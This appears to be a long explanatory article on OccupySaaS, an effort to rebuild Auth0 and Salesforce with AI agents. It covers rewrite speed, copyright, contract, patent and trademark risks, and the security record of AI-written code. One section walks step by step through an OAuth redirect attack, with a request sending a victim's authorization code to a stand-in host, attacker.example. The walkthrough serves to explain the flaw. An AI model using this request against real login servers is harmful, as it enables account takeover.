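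AI has also produced many poor copies. The website decomp.dev, which tracked projects to reverse engineer video games, announced on 15 October that it was closing. Its administrator, quoted in *Video Game Reverse Engineering Community Shuts Down* (Koebler, 2026), complains that opportunists take volunteers' unfinished work and release a "half-baked, barely-functional port". The administrator accepts that AI speeds up the work considerably when people guide it and review the code.

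Models are quickly getting better at reverse-engineering compiled programs. SRE-Bench tests this with private programs that the models are unlikely to have seen in training. OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra solved 88.0% of the challenges on the first attempt, compared with 55.9% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol, according to Popular AI's *Frontier AI can now reverse-engineer software binaries* (2026). OccupySaaS can't benefit directly from this skill, because Auth0 and Salesforce never give customers the server program.

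### Clones of Adobe and Microsoft Office

Several AI-written clones of Adobe's design programs and Microsoft Office appeared within days of each other in October. Koebler calls them "mostly-functional" and notes that the originals cost hundreds of dollars a year. According to TechSpot, one developer began making free Adobe clones out of frustration with cancellation fees. Tom's Hardware describes ArtCraft, the Adobe alternative, as part of the same backlash against subscriptions.

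"Mostly functional" is a reporter's impression, not a test score. A Photoshop clone might crop a holiday photo correctly but move all the text when it opens a designer's poster. The developers could check by opening thousands of files in both programs and comparing the pictures. Until someone publishes such results, the clones are good evidence that AI can quickly produce a convincing first version, but weak evidence that a designer could switch to one.

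### Working from a description

OccupySaaS's agents work from a specification, so they have less to go on than any of these projects did. *Fable 5 wrote a Windows kernel in 38 minutes* describes how Claude Fable 5 started with an empty folder, then planned and wrote a kernel modelled on that of Windows. A kernel is the core of an operating system, which shares out memory and processor time among programs. The finished kernel started up on a simulated computer and passed 14 tests.

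Those tests were built into the kernel and check, for example, that it can allocate memory. A kernel could pass all 14 and still be unable to run a single Windows program. Sanfilippo's Z80 emulator was a much smaller project, but it could be tested much better because other people had already written demanding tests for that processor.

Cloudflare's project is closer to what OccupySaaS is doing. BestHub reports that the company used AI to rewrite the core of the API of Next.js, the framework behind the bicycle shop's website, in a week. Next.js is open source, though, so anyone who wants to copy its behaviour can consult its code and tests.

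### Is OccupySaaS unusually fast?

OccupySaaS has written code at about the same pace as GitHub and much more slowly than Sumner:

| Project | What the builders could see | Lines of new code | Time | Lines a day |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Sentry, 2021, before AI agents | Source code | 95,000 | 1.5 years | 170 |
| GitHub Copilot | Source code | 800,000 | 14.5 weeks | 8,000 |
| Bun | Source code | 1,009,000 | 11 days | 92,000 |
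| OccupySaaS | Documentation and behaviour | 150,000 | 3 weeks | 7,000 |

The comparison is rough. A translator can follow the original's design line by line, while OccupySaaS had to design its own programs, so its pace is more impressive than it looks in the table. However, Sumner and GitHub were replacing software that people relied on every day, so their versions had to work. Claude Code, which many programmers use daily, has run on the Rust version of Bun since June.

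Sumner and GitHub each spent about 15 or 16 cents on AI for each line of new code, not counting salaries. At that rate, OccupySaaS's 150,000 lines would have cost about $24,000, though this is only an estimate because the founders haven't said what they spend. An unemployed engineer might struggle to pay that much, but a flat-rate subscription like the ones Heumann used could cost much less.

### How agents do when no test can check the work

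If automatic checks matter this much, agents should do worse on work that only a person can judge. Epoch AI, a research group that measures AI progress, has tested models on its own staff's tasks, such as graphic design and planning research projects. Hong, Burnham and Bye (2026) explain in *We tried to automate Epoch* that ordinary benchmarks often include only easily graded tasks, which makes AI look more useful than it is. Epoch's staff graded the models by hand, to the standard they expect of a colleague. The two best models, Claude Fable 5.1 and GPT-6 Astra, averaged 65% in October.

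Three weeks later, Hong reported on six models, including two newer ones, in *How good are Fable 5.2 and GPT-6.2 Astra at real work?* None met Epoch's standard for an employee, not even the two that lead Epoch's index of AI capabilities. In Heumann's project, agents sometimes marked tasks as finished without checking them thoroughly. An agent that does this will stop too early unless something outside it reports a failure.

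But Epoch's tasks differ from programming in many ways besides lacking a test, so the study can't show that the missing test causes the lower scores.

The successes may also make automatic checks look more capable than they are. Sumner and GitHub had good reasons to publish projects that worked, and a company whose agents failed a good test suite for three months would be less likely to write about it. Heumann's account is valuable partly because he describes a month that went wrong.

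### Which of OccupySaaS's gaps are likely to close

For most of the features ZeroAuthy lacks, an agent would have something to test its work against. The OpenID Foundation has tests for back-channel logout, and the FIDO Alliance, the industry group behind passkeys, offers test tools for servers that accept them. SCIM is a public standard that specifies each request and response. An agent can try Apple, GitHub and Facebook logins on the real services. The developers could probably add these features within weeks or months if they keep working at October's pace. SAML may take longer because companies' systems differ.

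The developers could also test ZeroAuthy by comparing it with Auth0. An agent would send the same request to both and treat any unexplained difference as a fault. OccupySaaS's rules allow such black-box tests, though Auth0's terms of service might not.

This kind of check is much slower than Sumner's. Since the move to Rust, Bun's developers have used an automatic tool to feed random input about 100 billion times to the parts of Bun that read code and data files. Sending that many requests to Auth0 would take more than 30 years at 100 a second, and Auth0 limits how many a customer can make. A login service needs far fewer tests, but the developers rebuilding Auth0 would still have to choose them carefully, and they couldn't learn Auth0's secret rules for spotting attacks this way.

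SalesCompel's most obvious gap, deal tracking, should be fairly easy to close. Salesforce publicly documents how its API handles opportunities and offers developers free accounts, so an agent could save the same opportunity in both systems and compare the stored records.

Even a copy of Apex could in principle be checked against the original. An agent could write thousands of short Apex programs, run them in a Salesforce account, record the results, and then build a version of the language that gives the same results. The translator of the OCaml runtime relied on a similar comparison but could also read the original code, so copying Apex without seeing its code would be harder. It would also take much longer than adding opportunities, because Apex programs depend on many other parts of Salesforce.

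Agents will have more trouble replacing what each customer has built. The bicycle wholesaler might want a new order screen that its salespeople can use while on the phone with a shop. An agent can test whether the screen saves the order, but someone has to watch the salespeople use it to see whether it slows them down. Building this screen is closer to the work Epoch tested than to translating Bun.

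## Is it legal to copy a service this way?

Copyright law in the United States and Europe probably allows what OccupySaaS does, as long as its programs contain none of the vendors' code or text. The developers face a bigger risk from patents, which a clean room doesn't protect against, and from the terms they accept when they open a test account. No court has ruled on the project. The applicable law depends partly on where the founders live, which they haven't disclosed.

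The project argues on its home page that "Interoperating with an API is not the same as copying a product." That is true, but ZeroAuthy is also meant to replace Auth0. BornCity reports that the founders cite two precedents, Phoenix's BIOS and the US Supreme Court's 2021 decision in *Google v. Oracle*. IBM never took Phoenix to court over the BIOS, so only *Google v. Oracle* is a legal precedent.

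### What Google v. Oracle decided

Google wanted Android to be familiar to programmers who knew the Java language, so it copied about 11,500 lines from Java's API. These lines named ready-made functions and set out how they were organised. Google wrote its own code to carry out the functions, but Oracle, which owned Java, sued over the copied lines.

Google won by six votes to two. The Supreme Court left open whether copyright covers an API, though people often cite the case as proof that nobody can own one. The Court assumed for the sake of argument that copyright covered the 11,500 lines, and held that copying them was fair use, the American exception for certain kinds of unlicensed copying. An appeals court had ruled earlier in the case that copyright did cover them.

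OccupySaaS would therefore have to argue fair use too, or persuade a court that the parts it copied aren't protected. Two of the four factors that judges weigh in a fair-use case favour the project. An API is functional, so it gets weaker protection than a novel. The project also needs to copy very little of it. To imitate the request for a customer's last login, ZeroAuthy would need to copy an address, a field name and an error code, but none of the code behind them.

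The other two factors, the purpose of the copying and its effect on the market, are harder for OccupySaaS to argue. Google used Java's function names in a new kind of product, the smartphone, where Oracle had had little success. ZeroAuthy does the same job as Auth0 for the same customers, and its developers openly hope those customers will leave Auth0. Okta could argue that copyright exists to prevent this kind of harm.

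The best answer to that argument comes from a case about a direct substitute. In 1999 Connectix sold a program that let people play PlayStation games on a computer, without Sony's console. Its engineers had copied Sony's BIOS while studying it, but the finished program contained none of Sony's code. In 2000 the Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, ruled that the copying was fair use and treated Sony's lost console sales as the result of legitimate competition. OccupySaaS is in a stronger position in one respect, since it never had the vendors' server code to copy.

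### The European rule

European law is clearer because of a very similar case. SAS Institute sells statistical software, and its customers write their own programs in the SAS language. World Programming, a small British company, built a cheaper product that could run those programs. It had no access to SAS's source code and worked from the manuals and a copy of the software it had bought to study.

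The EU Court of Justice ruled in 2012 that copyright in a program doesn't cover what the program does, the programming language, or the format of its data files. The judges reasoned that if it did, somebody could monopolise an idea. The EU Software Directive, the law they were interpreting, also excludes the ideas and principles behind a program's interfaces from copyright. Cornelißen therefore calls copying an API the unproblematic part of OccupySaaS's work.

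SAS also sued in the United States, where an appeals court rejected its copyright claim in 2023 because SAS hadn't shown which parts of its software were protected. American courts may well reach the same result as European ones, but a defendant in the United States has to spend much more on lawyers.

### The wording of the manual

A manual is a separate work from the software, and copyright protects its wording even when anyone is free to copy the functions it describes. World Programming won the dispute over its software, but an English court found that its manual had copied too much from SAS's manuals.

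OccupySaaS may build a setting that Auth0's documentation describes and explain it in its own words. If an AI agent pastes Auth0's explanation into ZeroAuthy's help pages, that is copying, even if the agent changes a few words. Field names and error codes are safer to reuse because a compatible program can't work without them.

In Auth0's terms, Okta also claims exclusive ownership of the site's content. ConductAtlas' *Site content owned exclusively by Okta* records this clause and counts similar ones at 259 of the 352 online services it tracks. The clause makes little difference here, because Okta already owns the text of its documentation and can't gain ownership of the facts in it by claiming the page.

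Auth0's SDKs are less of a problem than its documentation. Auth0 publishes most of them under the MIT licence, which lets anyone reuse the code if they keep the copyright notice. If an agent has reproduced a passage from one of these, the developers can keep it by adding the notice.

The same goes for much of the code an agent might have memorised from other free login servers. Ory Hydra, for example, uses the Apache-2.0 licence, as ZeroAuthy does. But ZITADEL moved in 2025 to the AGPL, a copyleft licence, which requires anyone who distributes a modified version to release it on the same terms. If ZeroAuthy contained a long passage from a recent ZITADEL release, the project would have to remove it or change its own licence.

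*Vibe-Coding* (Schebitz, 2026) lists code memorised by AI models as one of the legal limits on AI-written software in Germany. A Munich court ruled in November 2025 that song lyrics memorised by OpenAI's models counted as copies, and the same reasoning could extend to code.

A group of anonymous American GitHub contributors had less success when they sued OpenAI and Microsoft because AI models produced code similar to theirs without their names and copyright notices. They made the novel claim that this violated a section of the Digital Millennium Copyright Act (DMCA) that forbids removing such notices. The Ninth Circuit rejected the claim in September, Mullin (2026) reports in *Victory! Appeals Court Rejects Expansive New Copyright Claim* for the Electronic Frontier Foundation, a digital rights group that had argued for that result. The developer of another login server could still sue OccupySaaS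 for ordinary copying.

### Chardet and other disputes over AI rewrites

The dispute over chardet, the Python library that Claude rewrote in March, is the best-known test of these rules so far, though nobody had taken it to court when lawyers and journalists commented on it. Chardet had always been under the LGPL, a copyleft licence, but its maintainer, Dan Blanchard, released the rewrite under the MIT licence over the objections of Mark Pilgrim, the original author.

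According to Meeker, an open-source lawyer, Blanchard answered by citing a plagiarism checker, which found that the new version shared less than 1.3% of its structure with any earlier release. Corbet (2026), in *The relicensing of chardet*, explains why this doesn't settle the matter. If a model had translated chardet into the programming language Lisp, the two versions would look quite different, yet most people would agree that the Lisp version came from the original.

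Richard Fontana, who helped write version 3 of the LGPL, sided with Blanchard. He saw no basis for requiring the LGPL because nobody had identified protected material from the old versions of chardet in the new one (quoted in Willison, 2026). Meeker thinks this is probably right. If so, a program whose builders never saw the original code should be easier to defend than chardet, whose maintainer had worked on the old code for over a decade.

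Other disputes have followed the same pattern. According to the abstract of *Let's end open source together with this one simple trick*, a talk at the European open-source conference FOSDEM, the database company MongoDB used an AI agent in 2025 to recreate thousands of lines of copyleft code and release them under the Apache license, and the prompts were still in the repository. In court, prompts like these would be valuable evidence for the original author if they included an instruction to "rewrite this file", or for the defendant if they contained only a specification.

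Screen designs and icons can have their own copyright, even where functions don't. This matters for ArtCraft, the set of free alternatives to Adobe's programs, because the copies look confusingly similar to the originals, according to Miller-Aichholz (2026) in *Ein Entwickler kopiert mit KI die Programme von Software-Platzhirschen*. ArtCraft's developer also describes his work as clean-room. Guadamuz (2026), in *Recreating Adobe*, accepts that one of the programs draws on Adobe's published specification for Photoshop files, but notes that much about the process remains unclear. OccupySaaS mostly avoids the issue of copied designs, because most of ZeroAuthy is a server without screens and the project allows no copied artwork in SalesCompel's screens.

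### The terms of a test account

Unlike copyright, which applies to everybody, a contract applies only to people who have agreed to it. The specification writer described earlier had to accept the vendor's terms to open the trial account she used to see what a login service returns for a customer who has never logged in.

Salesforce's standard customer agreement has for years barred customers from reverse engineering the service or using it to build a competing product, except where the law gives them the right. Versions of Okta's agreement have contained similar bans. Free developer accounts can have separate terms, and vendors revise all these terms, so the version the tester accepted is the one that matters. Under a clause like Salesforce's, her experiment could be a breach of contract, even though she learned only that a field can be empty.

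World Programming had the right to copy the functions of SAS's software, but it was held liable for breaching the licence when it studied them. The company had clicked to accept terms that banned reverse engineering and limited how it could use the software. SAS sued in North Carolina, and a jury awarded it $26.4 million. State law on unfair business practices tripled that to $79 million, and an appeals court upheld the award in 2017. The jury had also found fraud in the way World Programming obtained the software, so an honest tester with a free account should face much less.

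The EU's Software Directive lets anyone entitled to use a copy of a program observe, study and test how it works, and a contract can't take that right away. World Programming benefited from this rule, but it had a copy of SAS's software on its own computers, whereas an Auth0 customer never receives a copy of Auth0. The directive's wording favours the vendor, so a court could decide that the right doesn't extend to rented services. It could also decide that it would be absurd for customers to lose the right because the vendor kept the program.

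Here is how this affects the people around the project:

| What the person does | Has she accepted the vendor's terms? |
|---|---|
| Reads public documentation without an account | Usually not, though a website can have terms of its own |
| Runs Auth0's open-source SDKs against ZeroAuthy | Only the SDK's licence |
| Opens a trial account to test Auth0's responses | Yes |
| Pays for Auth0 and reports to the project how ZeroAuthy differs | Yes, through her company's contract |
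| Installs ZeroAuthy without ever using Auth0 | No |

Much of the work can therefore avoid these contracts, because neither program's compatibility laboratory needs an account with the vendor. But the project also allows black-box test results, and the most useful ones come from the real service. If contributors used test accounts to get them, the records the project promises to keep would help defend it against a copyright claim but would also document the breach of contract.

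A customer who helps the project could be at more risk than its founders, because Okta knows who she is. If the bicycle shop runs the same login through both services and publishes the differences, Okta might treat that as using Auth0 for a competitor's benefit. Okta seems unlikely to sue a bicycle shop, but it could close the shop's account. A company that only wants to check whether its own website works on ZeroAuthy has a much better excuse.

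Okta's terms can't stop the code from spreading, because someone who merely downloads ZeroAuthy hasn't agreed to them. To act against that person, Okta would need a claim under copyright, patent or trade secret law.

Using an AI agent to run the tests doesn't remove the tester's responsibility. In August the Ninth Circuit ruled that the user who directs an AI agent, not the company that made it, "accesses" a website under US computer-crime law, at least when the traffic passes through the user's own computer. Cooley's *Ninth Circuit Rules on AI Agent ‘Access’ to Third-Party Websites Under CFAA* (2026) adds that websites may enforce their terms of service instead. In this case, that would mean Okta enforcing its terms against the tester.

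OccupySaaS also has to follow Anthropic's rules as long as it depends on Claude. Gerke reports in *Neue Regeln für Claude Code* that Anthropic has restricted the use of its coding agent to rebuild well-known video games. A similar rule for business software would force the developers to switch to another model, even if a court found their work legal.

### What former employees know

The founders' ban on using confidential knowledge from former employees roughly follows American and European law. An engineer may use her general skills in a new job, including what she has learned about building login systems, but not her former employer's trade secrets. These are valuable facts that the company has taken reasonable steps to keep private.

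Auth0's rules for spotting suspicious logins are probably trade secrets. OccupySaaS may work out similar rules from public sources, because independent discovery is lawful. But if a former Auth0 engineer remembers how many failed logins in what period cause the service to block an address, and writes those numbers into ZeroAuthy's specification, Okta could sue her. It could also sue whoever runs the project, if they knew or should have known where the numbers came from.

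The written rule would help the founders show good faith only if somebody enforces it. dasarpai's *from claw code to clean room* says that a clean-room label on GitHub is not a defence. Courts would want to know who wrote each part of the specification and where they used to work. An anonymous project could hardly answer without identifying its contributors.

A leak of a secret would also be hard to undo. Okta could ask a judge to order the secret's removal, but once it has been in a public repository for a few weeks, people all over the world may have copies.

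### Patents

Even a perfect clean room is no defence against a patent claim. An engineer who independently invents and uses a patented method infringes the patent, even without having heard of it.

Okta (2025) publishes a list of its patents by product, which helps it claim damages from infringers. The list includes two for Auth0, "Facilitating Single Sign-on to Software Applications" and "Secure Single Sign-on to Software Applications". The patents are probably narrower than these titles suggest. A patent's reach depends on its numbered claims, and a program infringes a claim only if it does everything the claim describes. Nobody has published a comparison between these claims and ZeroAuthy's code.

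The project has some protection against patent claims. Companies that help write the OpenID standards promise not to assert patents that others need to follow those standards, which makes the standard login safer to copy than Auth0's own features. American courts have also struck down many software patents since 2014 for covering abstract ideas, but a defendant may have to pay for a long lawsuit before a judge rules on that question.

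Companies other than Okta could also sue. Biogy, a security company, owns a US patent on one-time passwords that depend on the time. It wrote to customers of Okta and Microsoft, including the supermarket chain Albertsons, claiming that the products they used infringed the patent. Okta and Microsoft sued Biogy in April 2025 for a ruling that they didn't infringe, according to Bloomberg Law's *Okta, Microsoft Sue Password Protection System Patent Owner* (2025). The cases ended in March 2026. Bloomberg Law's *Okta, Microsoft Drop Suits Against Cybersecurity Patent Owner* (2026) reports that Biogy agreed not to assert the patent against Okta or its customers.

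That promise covers the bicycle shop while it pays for Auth0. If the shop moves to ZeroAuthy, which also offers one-time passwords, it is no longer an Okta customer for its logins and can't count on the promise. A small shop is an unlikely target, but Biogy did write to a supermarket chain. Apache-2.0 gives users a licence to any relevant patents that the contributors own, but not to patents owned by Biogy or Okta. The licence also disclaims all warranties. The shop would have to defend itself, whereas Okta's customers had Okta's lawyers to go to court first.

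### The names ZeroAuthy and SalesCompel

OccupySaaS may legally write that ZeroAuthy replaces Auth0, because trademark law allows people to use another company's product name to refer to that product, as long as they don't suggest that the company endorses them. Okta also uses other companies' names, and its *Copyright and Trademarks* acknowledges the names and logos of GitHub, Salesforce and others. OccupySaaS states on its home page that no vendor endorses it and that it uses product names only to describe compatibility.

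The names of the project's own two programs are riskier than those references. "ZeroAuthy" reverses the two parts of "Auth0", and "SalesCompel" replaces the "force" in "Salesforce" with a word of similar meaning. American courts ask whether ordinary buyers are likely to be confused about who makes a product, and they compare the sound, look and meaning of the names as well as the products.

OccupySaaS uses puns as brand names, and the joke may not protect it. In 2023 the US Supreme Court ruled against special protection for a dog toy that imitated a Jack Daniel's whiskey bottle, because the maker was using the joke as its own brand. The judges decided only that the usual trademark test applied, not whether the toy was unlawful. Salesforce could also bring a claim under dilution law, which protects famous names even when nobody is confused.

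"ZeroAuthy" also contains the name "Authy", which belongs to Twilio, a company the project has no dispute with. Twilio's *Authy* describes an app and an API for securing logins with one-time codes. Twilio merged the API into another product years ago but kept the app. ZeroAuthy is also login software and offers one-time codes, so a programmer could reasonably take it for a Twilio product. But programmers choose login software with some care, and "auth" is a common abbreviation that Twilio can't claim as its own. It is unclear whether enough people would be confused, and there is no public sign that Twilio has complained.

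The programs' names are the easiest legal problem to fix, because the developers could change both in an afternoon. At least they didn't release their rewrites as new versions of the originals, as Blanchard did with chardet. Corbet thinks a new name for Blanchard's rewrite would have upset far fewer people.

### Who owns code that Claude wrote?

American copyright protects only what a human has created. The computer scientist Stephen Thaler tried to register a picture with his AI system as its only author, and the courts ruled against him. The Supreme Court declined to hear his appeal on 2 March 2026 (Mills, 2026, *Supreme Court Lets Stand Ruling That Bars AI Copyright*), which left the ruling in place without the Court deciding the question itself. The case also didn't settle how copyright applies when a person and a model work together, which is how people write most AI-assisted software.

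The US Copyright Office concluded in a January 2025 report that a person who uses AI as a tool keeps the copyright in whatever she contributes, but that prompts alone don't give her enough control to make her the author of the result. She can also hold copyright in the way she selects and arranges AI-made parts. Mills gives the example of *Zarya of the Dawn*, a comic book whose author got copyright in her text and in the arrangement of the pages, but not in the AI-generated pictures.

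By this standard, probably only parts of ZeroAuthy have copyright. Specifications that people wrote have it, and the overall design may too, if a person made the creative decisions. A function that Claude wrote from the specification and a reviewer approved without changes probably doesn't. The commit history can't show exactly which parts have copyright.

Apache-2.0 requires anyone who passes the code on to include the licence, keep the copyright notices and mark the files they have changed. These requirements depend on copyright, so the founders would have little basis to sue if Okta copied a function written entirely by Claude into Auth0 and removed the notices.

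This matters less for a project that wants people to use its code freely than it would for a business. Law360's *'Vibe Coding' Pushes Cos. To Rethink Copyright Protection* reports that companies now document what their engineers contribute and rely more on trade secrets. OccupySaaS publishes everything, so it can't rely on trade secrets, but it hardly needs them. It mainly stands to lose credit for its work. Blanchard reached a similar conclusion about chardet and switched it from MIT to 0BSD, a licence that doesn't even require a notice.

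Claude can't own the code it writes, but that doesn't help users if the code infringes somebody else's rights. If Claude reproduces a passage it memorised from another login server, the passage still belongs to that server's copyright holders. Releasing the code under the Apache-2.0 licence doesn't change this, because the founders can only license what they own.

### What Okta and Salesforce have done

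By early December 2026, neither Okta nor Salesforce appeared to have commented publicly on OccupySaaS or taken legal action against it. They may not see the project as a threat, since its login server is unfinished and its CRM can't record a sale. A lawsuit would also give the protest more publicity than it could get on its own. Their silence doesn't mean they consent, and they could still sue.

If the companies did sue, they would have to identify the defendants. American courts let a company sue unknown people and then demand their details from services that may have them, such as GitHub, the chat service Discord and the three donation platforms. The OpenID Foundation probably has a name too, from the certification form.

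If Okta finds copied code or text, it can send GitHub a takedown notice under the DMCA, which is cheaper than suing. GitHub normally removes the material without waiting for a court. To get it back, the developers would have to send a counter-notice with a name, address and telephone number, and agree that they can be sued. An anonymous founder might prefer to leave the code offline, even with a good defence. But a takedown notice has to allege copyright infringement, so Okta couldn't properly use one over a breach of its terms or patent infringement. A company that knowingly makes a false claim may have to pay damages.

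## Who would keep the free versions secure and maintained?

For now, security and maintenance would fall mostly to one anonymous developer using AI agents, and no contract obliges that person to do the work. The collective tells companies not to run either program in production yet. BornCity attributes this to ZeroAuthy's lack of official security certificates, but a certificate wouldn't determine who fixes flaws found later.

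### Why a login server is a severe test

A flaw in a login server can expose every program that relies on it, while a flaw in most other programs exposes only that program's data. If SalesCompel had a hole, a thief might copy the bicycle wholesaler's customer list. But the wholesaler's order system, staff rota and payroll program may all use one login server to identify users. They accept any valid token with that server's signature, so a thief who steals the signing key can forge a token that identifies him as the head of payroll.

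A company can keep its payroll program off the public internet, but its login page has to be open to customers, which also exposes it to attackers. Even specialists make mistakes in login software. The former security architect of ForgeRock, a vendor of login systems, says its OAuth server had hundreds of security bugs even though the company ran hundreds of thousands of automated tests on every change.

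### How one missing check loses an account

Suppose the bicycle shop's login server doesn't check whether the shop has registered the return address. A customer logged in to the shop's phone app yesterday, and her browser still holds the server's cookie. Like many others, the server doesn't ask her to approve the same app twice.

1. She opens a web page that an attacker controls, perhaps from a link about a cycling race. The page sends her browser to the shop's real login server with this request:

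```
GET /authorize
  response_type = code
  client_id = bikeshop-app
  redirect_uri = https://attacker.example/collect
  code_challenge = (made from the attacker's own verifier)
  code_challenge_method = S256
```

2. The server finds yesterday's cookie and doesn't ask for a password. It creates a code for her account and sends her browser to the attacker's address with it.
3. The attacker submits the code to `/oauth/token` with his own verifier. For the return address, he gives the app's genuine one, which is on the shop's list.
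4. The verifier matches the challenge, so the server gives him tokens for her account.

He can now read her orders or have her next bicycle delivered somewhere else. She typed nothing, so a strong password or a one-time code wouldn't have helped. PKCE wouldn't have helped either, because the attacker started the login and made the secret himself. The server could have stopped him at the start by checking one address against a list.

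### The same mistake in Cloudflare's library

Cloudflare, whose network carries traffic for many websites, made this mistake in 2025 in an open-source library for building OAuth servers. The library is the closest comparison to ZeroAuthy because Claude wrote most of it. Its main developer, Kenton Varda, writes in the README, reproduced on the software index Ecosyste.ms, that he expected terrible code he could laugh at but found it surprisingly good. He adds that security experts reviewed every line and compared it with the standards.

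Varda estimated that the library took a few days with AI and would have taken weeks, perhaps months, to write by hand (Willison, 2025). He called it "a pretty ideal use case" because the standard was well known and the API was clearly specified. AI had saved him little time on Cloudflare's own, more unusual code.

The library checked the return address only when an app exchanged its code for tokens. That is too late, because the attacker can supply the genuine address at that point. The security advisory, GitLab's *GHSA-7cp4-jw97-3rc2* (2025), rates the flaw as medium, partly because the attack works only on servers that approve returning users automatically. In the advisory, the library's author admits to having known about the rule and thought about it a lot while designing the library, but then forgetting to make sure the check was in the library.

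A second flaw let an attacker make the library skip its PKCE check, according to OSV's *GHSA-qgp8-v765-qxx9* (2025). Cloudflare fixed both in version 0.0.5 and published the advisories on 1 May 2025. The vulnerability tracker stack.watch listed no new vulnerabilities in the library for the first months of 2026 on its page *CloudFlare Workers Oauth Provider*.

Varda caught another serious mistake. He had asked Claude to encrypt stored data so that only someone with a valid token could read it. Claude made the encryption key from a SHA-256 hash of the token. But the library already stored that hash next to the encrypted data, as the token's ID, so anyone who copied the database could have decrypted it. The code would have passed any test that only encrypted the data and read it back. Varda saw the problem because he understood the cryptography, but many programmers would have missed it.

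Ory's *Cloudflare, please don't vibe code your own crypto* criticises the finished library too, though Ory sells competing login software. Ory's founder objects that the library's public code contains a fixed value used to derive encryption keys. This seems less serious than he suggests, since an attacker would still need both a token and a copy of the stored data. His better objection is that reviewers may spend hours understanding a large amount of generated code, only for the next prompt to change it.

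ZeroAuthy probably doesn't have the redirect flaw, because the OpenID tests check for it, but those tests might miss a faulty PKCE check. Cloudflare was otherwise better placed to avoid such flaws. It has a security team, and it released a much smaller library than ZeroAuthy under its own name, but two basic checks still failed.

### How often AI-written code has holes

AI agents write working code much more reliably than secure code. *Last Secure Code Benchmark* (2026), from researchers in Singapore and at Alibaba, tested six leading agents on 450 tasks based on 150 real vulnerabilities. The agents had to complete a function, write a file or build a whole program from a specification that never mentioned security. Hidden tests checked whether the code worked and whether it was secure.

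Between 73.6% and 91.3% of the solutions worked, depending on the agent. The best agent, Claude Fable 5, produced working, secure code on 25.1% of the tasks. So for every agent in the study, about two thirds or more of the working solutions failed a security test.

These tasks are deliberately hard. Each comes from a security hole that programmers left in a real program. OccupySaaS's specification writers can also include security instructions, such as "refuse any return address that isn't on the list", but these may not be enough. The review *Beyond Passing Tests* (2026) describes SusVibes, another benchmark, in which most of the agents' working solutions were insecure even when the request hinted at the vulnerability. In BaxBench, which is closer to ZeroAuthy's case because the models write server programs, attacks succeeded against around half of the programs that worked correctly.

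The security company Veracode has tracked flaws in AI-generated code since 2025, when 45% of the code it tested contained a known kind of flaw. In July 2026, *AI-generated code security has stalled at 56%* (Constantin, 2026) reported that the share of secure results had barely moved after a year and more than 100 models. In October, Veracode (2026) announced an average of 62%, the first meaningful gain, with Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Sol both at 73%. Veracode sells security testing, so it benefits when people worry about these numbers.

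Vonk (2026), in *AI-written code is getting safer, mostly where it was easy*, looked at where the gain came from. Veracode had given 18 models ordinary programming requests in four languages and checked the code for four kinds of flaw. The models were already good at avoiding weak cryptography and SQL injection (typed text that the database runs as a command), and their scores on both hardly changed. Nearly all the improvement was in one category, which by elimination must be log injection, where an attacker plants false lines in a program's records.

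The models wrote code that prevented cross-site scripting only 18% of the time, up from 15% in July. In cross-site scripting, an attacker gets his own code to run in someone else's browser. This matters for ZeroAuthy because it provides its own login page, where such code could read each password as a customer typed it.

Studies of other code give different rates. *Broken by Default* (2026) gave 500 prompts to seven older models and found flaws in 55.8% of the results on average. Memory allocation was one of the worst areas, but it is less of a concern for ZeroAuthy, which is written in Go, a language that manages memory automatically. *Securing AI-Generated Code* (2026) cites a study of 7,703 files on GitHub that were credited to AI. Python had the highest rate, with a detectable weakness in 12.1% of files. This is lower than the rate in *Broken by Default*, probably because many ordinary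 files do nothing risky and automatic scanners miss some flaws.

*What is the Difference Between Me and You?* (2026) points out that benchmarks like these usually don't include code that people wrote for the same tasks. They therefore can't show whether a human team would have made ZeroAuthy safer.

### AI as a security reviewer

AI can also find security holes, including ones it made. A developer can ask a new agent session to attack ZeroAuthy, give it the return-address attack as an example, and have it turn every successful attack into a permanent test. Many rules in the OAuth standards are written as things a server "must" or "must not" do, so an agent could write at least one test for each, which would be tedious for a person.

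Anthropic's OSS Scanner is a free service that uses the company's strongest models to regularly search open-source projects for vulnerabilities. By October 2026, Anthropic had also manually reviewed more than 6,000 AI-generated reports from its wider scanning of open-source code. ZeroAuthy would be an obvious candidate for the service if enough people used it, but Anthropic says brand-new projects don't typically qualify. For now, the developers would have to pay for their own scans.

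Attackers can run the same kind of scan. ZeroAuthy's code is public, so anyone can ask a model to look for security flaws in it, whereas an outsider can only test Auth0's server by sending it requests. Open code is safer only if the people who find a flaw report it and somebody fixes it before an attacker uses it. A new project may have very few honest readers compared with a popular one.

### Too many reports and contributions

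Finding flaws has become so easy that fixing them is often the bottleneck. Alpha-Omega, a Linux Foundation project that funds open-source security, reports in its guide *Handling Your First GHSA* that 88,601 vulnerabilities were added to the public CVE catalogue between 1 January and 29 October 2026. That is more than twice as many as in the same period of 2025. Many of these are in open-source projects, where mostly unpaid volunteers check the reports and write the fixes. Anthropic acknowledges that reports already overwhelm many projects, and it designed its scanner for those that can keep up.

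Even a false security report takes time to check. Somebody might send ZeroAuthy a convincing three-page description of how to log in with an expired token. The maintainer has to set up a server and follow the steps, and may discover an hour later that the reporter's computer had the wrong date. He still has to check the next report, because it may be real.

Some projects have responded to the flood of AI-written code by refusing it. The free game engine Godot has banned AI-generated code from contributions (Seyfferth, 2026, *Godot und KI-Code*). The mapping program QGIS adopted a similar ban in October, and the terminal program Ghostty automatically closes submissions from first-time contributors (Cornelißen, 2026, *Freie KI-Nachbauten*). Langner (2026), in *KI-Verbot bei r/opensource*, contrasts the Linux kernel, which has dropped its label for AI-written code, with the Reddit forum r/opensource,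 which now excludes AI-assisted projects. OccupySaaS may therefore struggle to recruit volunteers on the forum, one of the most natural places to look for them.

PhotoCraft, a free imitation of Photoshop from the ArtCraft team, welcomed AI-written contributions. Cornelißen found that 310 people had contributed within two weeks of its release on 30 September. In one week the project accepted 1,725 sets of changes, an average of about ten an hour. In a sample of 100 that he checked, the same account had approved 99. A second account has since begun to help.

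Nobody can read code carefully at that rate. OccupySaaS promises that a human will review every change, so a rush of volunteers would force it to break that promise or leave most of their work waiting for review.

### Okta's breach in 2023

Paying a specialist doesn't guarantee safety either. In autumn 2023 an attacker had access to Okta's customer support system for nearly three weeks. Okta thought the most likely cause was that an employee had signed in to a personal Google account on a work laptop and saved the password for a support-system account in that Google account.

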